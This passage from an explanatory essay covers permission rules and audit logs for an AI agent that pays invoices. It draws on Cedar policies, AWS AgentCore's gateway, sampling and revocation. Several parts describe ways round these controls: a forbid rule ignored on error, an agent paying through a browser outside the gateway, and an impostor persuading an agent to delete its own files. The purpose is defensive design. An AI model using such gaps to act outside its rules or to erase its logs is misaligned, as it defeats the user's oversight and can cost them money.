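Input              sender line and full text of the invoice
Compared with      twelve earlier invoices, set no. 4
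Method             average cosine similarity
```

The software has to keep the full text of all thirteen invoices, because nobody can recompute the score without them. That is much more private data to protect than one address.

Suppose the provider withdraws version 2.1 in the spring. An auditor runs the same invoices through version 3.0 and gets 0.87, so the rule would no longer pay. The two versions may score the same invoices differently, so this doesn't show that the November payment was a mistake. The auditor can still confirm that 0.94 is above 0.90, but can't reproduce the 0.94. If a lookalike sender turns up later, nobody can test whether the November rule would have paid it.

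Some similarity checks don't have this problem. Edit distance is a fixed calculation, so it will give the same result in ten years. A skeleton comparison will too, if the record includes the Unicode version. A user who keeps a copy of an embedding model can also rerun it. A language model is less dependable even if the user keeps a copy, since Yan found that one gave the same tool different labels on different runs.

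### Rule B in Cedar

Cedar is an open-source language for permission rules, developed by Amazon Web Services (AWS), Amazon's cloud computing business. Cutler, Disselkoen and colleagues (2024), in *Cedar*, explain that when permissions are part of an application's code, an auditor has to read the code to find out who can do what. Cedar keeps the rules separate. Rule B might look like this:

```
permit (
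  principal == Agent::"assistant",
  action == Action::"pay_invoice",
  resource == Account::"northfield"
)
when {
  context.from == "accounts@northfield.example" &&
  context.dmarcPassDomain == "northfield.example" &&
  context.currency == "USD" &&
  context.amountInCents <= 18000 &&
  context.attemptsThisMonth == 0 &&
  context.attemptsLast14Days == 0 &&
  context.attemptsForMessage == 0 &&
  context.date < 20271001
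};
```

The principal is whoever is acting, and the resource is what they are acting on, here Northfield's saved bank account. The agent's software fills in the context values for each request. Cedar doesn't store earlier requests, so the software also has to count the payments.

Cutler and colleagues designed Cedar so that the same request, rules and stored data always produce the same decision. If the audit record includes all three inputs, an auditor can replay the decision years later.

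Cedar returns each decision with the names of the rules that determined it. For an approval, these are the "permit" rules whose conditions held. For a refusal, they are the "forbid" rules that applied, any one of which overrides every "permit" rule. Cedar also refuses a request that no rule covers, and then returns no rule names. Cedar can't answer "ask the user", but by checking for rule names, an agent's software can block the payment if a "forbid" rule applied and prompt the user if no rule did.

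The record should also include errors. *How We Built Cedar* (2024) explains that Cedar ignores a rule that produces an error. Consider a rule meant to block payments to any account the user hasn't saved:

```
forbid (principal, action == Action::"pay_invoice", resource)
unless { resource.saved };
```

If the software has no data on a forger's account, Cedar can't look up `saved`, so the rule produces an error and Cedar ignores the rule. Rule B still wouldn't pay the forger, because it names Northfield's account, but a careless "always allow" rule for `pay_invoice` would. Cedar's validator checks rules in advance, but its guarantee assumes the software has data on every account in the request. Changing the condition to `resource has saved && resource.saved` fixes the rule, because `has` returns false for a missing account. Cedar reports which rules produced errors, and the software should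 show a prompt whenever that list isn't empty.

### Why Cedar limits text matching

Cedar's `==` compares text exactly, so "Something" and "something" don't match. The only looser option for text is `like`, which lets an asterisk stand for any characters. In an example from Cedar's documentation, "Gotham" matches `"*ham"`. Similarly, a rule for `"*northfield.example"` would also accept accounts@notnorthfield.example. The user can avoid this by writing `"*@northfield.example"`, which accepts every address at northfield.example and no others.

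Cedar has no operator that changes capitals or reformats text. Cedar's *Security requirement* says the omission is intentional, partly because such operators disrupt automated reasoning about the rules. It adds that rule writers may be outside customers, who shouldn't have to work out the formatting. The application therefore has to standardize every value before passing it to Cedar. In the documentation's example, a "forbid" rule for an object fails if someone requests that object with its identifier in capitals.

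### Comparing rules before they take effect

These restrictions allow software to check every request a rule could allow, including requests nobody has made. AWS's *Introducing Cedar Analysis* describes a tool that turns two sets of rules into formulas and searches for a request that one set allows and the other refuses. If no such request exists, the tool has proved that the two sets are equivalent. For edits to Rule B, it would report:

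| Edit | Result |
|---|---|
| Put the conditions in a different order | Equivalent |
| Raise the limit from $180 to $200 | More permissive |
| Move the end date forward to June 2027 | Less permissive |
| Replace the saved address with billing@northfield.example | Incomparable |

"Incomparable" means that each version allows something the other refuses.

People can easily misjudge how an edit changes a rule. In AWS's *Why Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore chose Cedar for securing agentic workflows*, a shop gives bulk discounts on orders of 50 items or more, except for limited-edition products. Someone then limits the exception to orders of more than 200 items. The rule is longer and looks stricter, but the tool reports it as more permissive because an order of 73 limited-edition items now gets the discount.

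The tool can also find a rule that has no effect because another rule already allows everything it covers. If the user clicked "always allow" for `pay_invoice`, the tool would report that Rule B has no effect, and the user would learn that Rule B's limits no longer protect them.

The analysis is fast enough to run whenever someone saves a rule. Torlak, who works for AWS, reports in *SymCert* (2026) that each query took less than 20 milliseconds to generate and less than 40 to solve. The checks found possible mistakes in three of eight example applications, but eight applications are too few to show how common such mistakes are.

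A Cedar rule can use a similarity score if other software calculates it first:

```
context.similarityPercent >= 90
```

The analysis treats the score as a number that could take any value. It can prove that lowering the threshold to 85 makes the rule more permissive, but it can't identify any address that the change lets in. If the provider replaces the model, the rule's text stays the same, so the analysis reports that the two versions are equivalent even though they may accept different senders.

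An auditor can read an allowlist with one entry in a second. Software could print the 763 possible names one edit away from Northfield's, but few people would read them. At two edits, there are more than 140,000. An auditor has no practical way to list every message that an embedding model would score above 0.90.

### How an agent platform uses Cedar

Amazon Bedrock AgentCore is a service companies use to run AI agents. Its permission system, Policy, became generally available on March 3, 2026, according to AWS's *Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore is now generally available* (2026). A gateway between the agent and its tools blocks every call unless a Cedar rule permits it. The gateway also hides from the model any tool that the rules would always block.

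Administrators can describe a rule in ordinary language and have a model write it in Cedar. The platform then checks that the rule refers to real tools and looks for conditions that can never be met or that allow everything. These checks catch many drafting errors, but a well-formed rule with the wrong supplier's address would pass. AWS also runs the analysis when an administrator attaches rules to a gateway, and rejects all of them if it finds a logical error, such as two conflicting rules.

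According to AWS, a company can test its rules in a mode that records decisions without enforcing them. This would also suit Rule B. For three months, the user could keep answering prompts while the software records what the rule would have done. Any invoice that the rule would have paid but the user refused needs a closer look. The prompts must stay on during the trial because a rule in this mode blocks nothing.

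Classmethod's *[Update] Amazon Bedrock AgentCore Policy now supports Amazon Bedrock Guardrails* (2026) reports that since June, Policy has also worked with Guardrails, Amazon's filters for harmful or sensitive content, so not every check on the platform has to be an exact rule. When a filter affects a decision, the record should include the filter's version and result as well as the Cedar rule.

### When the log looks normal

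A clean log shows that the software followed the rule, but the rule itself may be bad. According to Cedar's documentation, each application is responsible for having rules that express the right permissions. If Northfield bills $180 for work it never did, the record looks exactly like the one for November. An invoice from a hijacked mailbox also leaves a normal record. To find such payments, the user needs evidence from outside the log, such as a yearly statement that Northfield sends by post.

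The log can also be incomplete. AgentCore's rules apply only to calls that go through its gateway, and any similar software has the same limit. If an agent can also use a browser where the user is logged in to the bank, it could pay someone without Rule B running. The user should compare the log with the bank statement to find such payments. A payment that the agent made but the log doesn't contain is more worrying than anything in the log, because the rules may never have checked it.

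The agent also shouldn't be able to change the log. In the experiment by Shapira and colleagues, an impostor persuaded the agent Ash to delete its own memory and settings files. An audit record in the same folder could have been deleted too. The software should write the log somewhere the agent can't access, or at least where the agent can only add lines.

Mathematical proofs help with only part of this. Michael and Roesner found that none of the 21 permission systems they reviewed has a proof that its enforcement is correct. Cedar comes closer. Cutler and colleagues proved important properties of its design and tested the working program against a formal model, which exposed nearly two dozen bugs. But the proofs don't cover the software that reads the From address and passes it to Cedar.

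### Measuring the errors of a scored rule

An auditor can estimate how often a similarity rule is wrong by checking a random sample of its decisions by hand, even though nobody can list everything the rule accepts. The same method works for exact-match rules, where it can reveal an entry that was wrong from the start.

The difficulty is the number of decisions an auditor needs. If a rule wrongly pays a share *p* of invoices, the chance that *n* randomly chosen payments are all correct is (1 − *p*)ⁿ. To show with 95% confidence that the error rate is below *p*, the auditor needs a sample with no errors that is large enough to bring this chance down to 5%:

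```
(1 - p)^n = 0.05,   so n is about 3/p
```

For the original Rule B and an attentive user, acting without asking was worthwhile only if fewer than 0.05% of invoices were bad. Showing that the rate is this low would take about 6,000 payments without an error. Rule B makes twelve payments a year, so reaching that number would take the user 500 years. A large company could collect enough payments in a few weeks, and checking them at ten seconds each would cost about $600.

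Filing choir notices is much easier to test, because a 5% error rate would be acceptable. Sixty correct decisions are enough, and the user can check them in ten minutes.

The calculation covers only the kind of mail in the sample. Six thousand honest invoices don't show how the rule would handle forged messages written to fit it. To find that out, testers have to write their own attacks and repeat the tests each time the model changes. Sampling therefore suits frequent, low-stakes decisions, but it can't justify using similarity for one household's payments.

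### A review routine

Reviewing a rule can cost more than the rule saves. Rule B saves at most $1.20 of the user's time a year, but a five-minute review costs $3, so reviewing it separately every month would cost $36 a year. It makes more sense to review all the rules together, perhaps when the user is reading the bank statement anyway. For a programmer whose rules save $10 of time a day, five minutes of review a month is small by comparison.

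The software should do most of the work and show only what needs a decision:

- **Rules about to end.** For Rule B, the software could show "12 payments, $2,160 in total, last used September 1" and ask whether to renew it.
- **Unused entries.** The software can suggest removing these, since a mistaken removal leads to only one extra prompt.
- **Edits.** The software should show who changed each rule and whether the change made it more permissive.
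- **Near misses.** These are requests that failed on a single point, such as the sender or the frequency, even if two of the rule's conditions check that point.

Near misses are especially useful because the point on which a request failed often suggests what happened:

| Why the request failed | Possible cause | What to do |
|---|---|---|
| Amount is $185 | Northfield raised its price | Confirm the price and change the limit |
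| Second invoice in a month | A duplicate, or extra work | Compare the two invoices |
| Different bank account | Fraud, or a new bank | Phone Northfield on a known number |
| Sender is northfie1d.example | A lookalike | Block the address |

Cedar's output identifies whole rules but not the conditions within them, so the software must test each condition separately to produce this report. For a similarity rule, the report should also include payments that scored just above the threshold, since a small change in the model could have reversed those decisions.

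### Undoing actions and withdrawing rules

If the user finds that a rule has been wrong since August, they need to stop it and reverse what it has already done. Because each record includes the rule's name and version, the software can list every action the rule allowed, and the user can deal with them together. For Rule A, the record should also include the meeting's identifier so that the software can cancel the right meeting.

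A bank transfer is harder to reverse, and the user may have to ask Northfield for a refund. The software could notify the user and wait until the next morning to send the money, so the user has time to cancel. A routine invoice can usually wait a day. The notice needs no answer, so it interrupts the user less than a prompt does, but it doesn't protect a user who ignores it.

Withdrawing a rule may not stop everything it has already approved. Li and colleagues note that MCP defines no way to revoke a permission, so each application has to provide its own. Zhou and Zhang warn that a queued action can outlast its approval, and that a second agent may continue work that the first handed over. If the software holds payments overnight, it must check Rule B again just before sending the money. Otherwise it could pay an invoice the morning after the user deleted the rule.

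Another rule may also allow the same payment. After the user deletes Rule B, the software can replay the November request with its original values and confirm that it now triggers a prompt. This tests only one request. To check every possible payment to Northfield, the software can use Cedar's analysis to compare the remaining rules with a copy that also forbids all such payments. If the two are equivalent, the remaining rules already allow no payment to Northfield. If they differ, the analysis gives an example of a payment that is still allowed, and the user can look for the rule that allows it.
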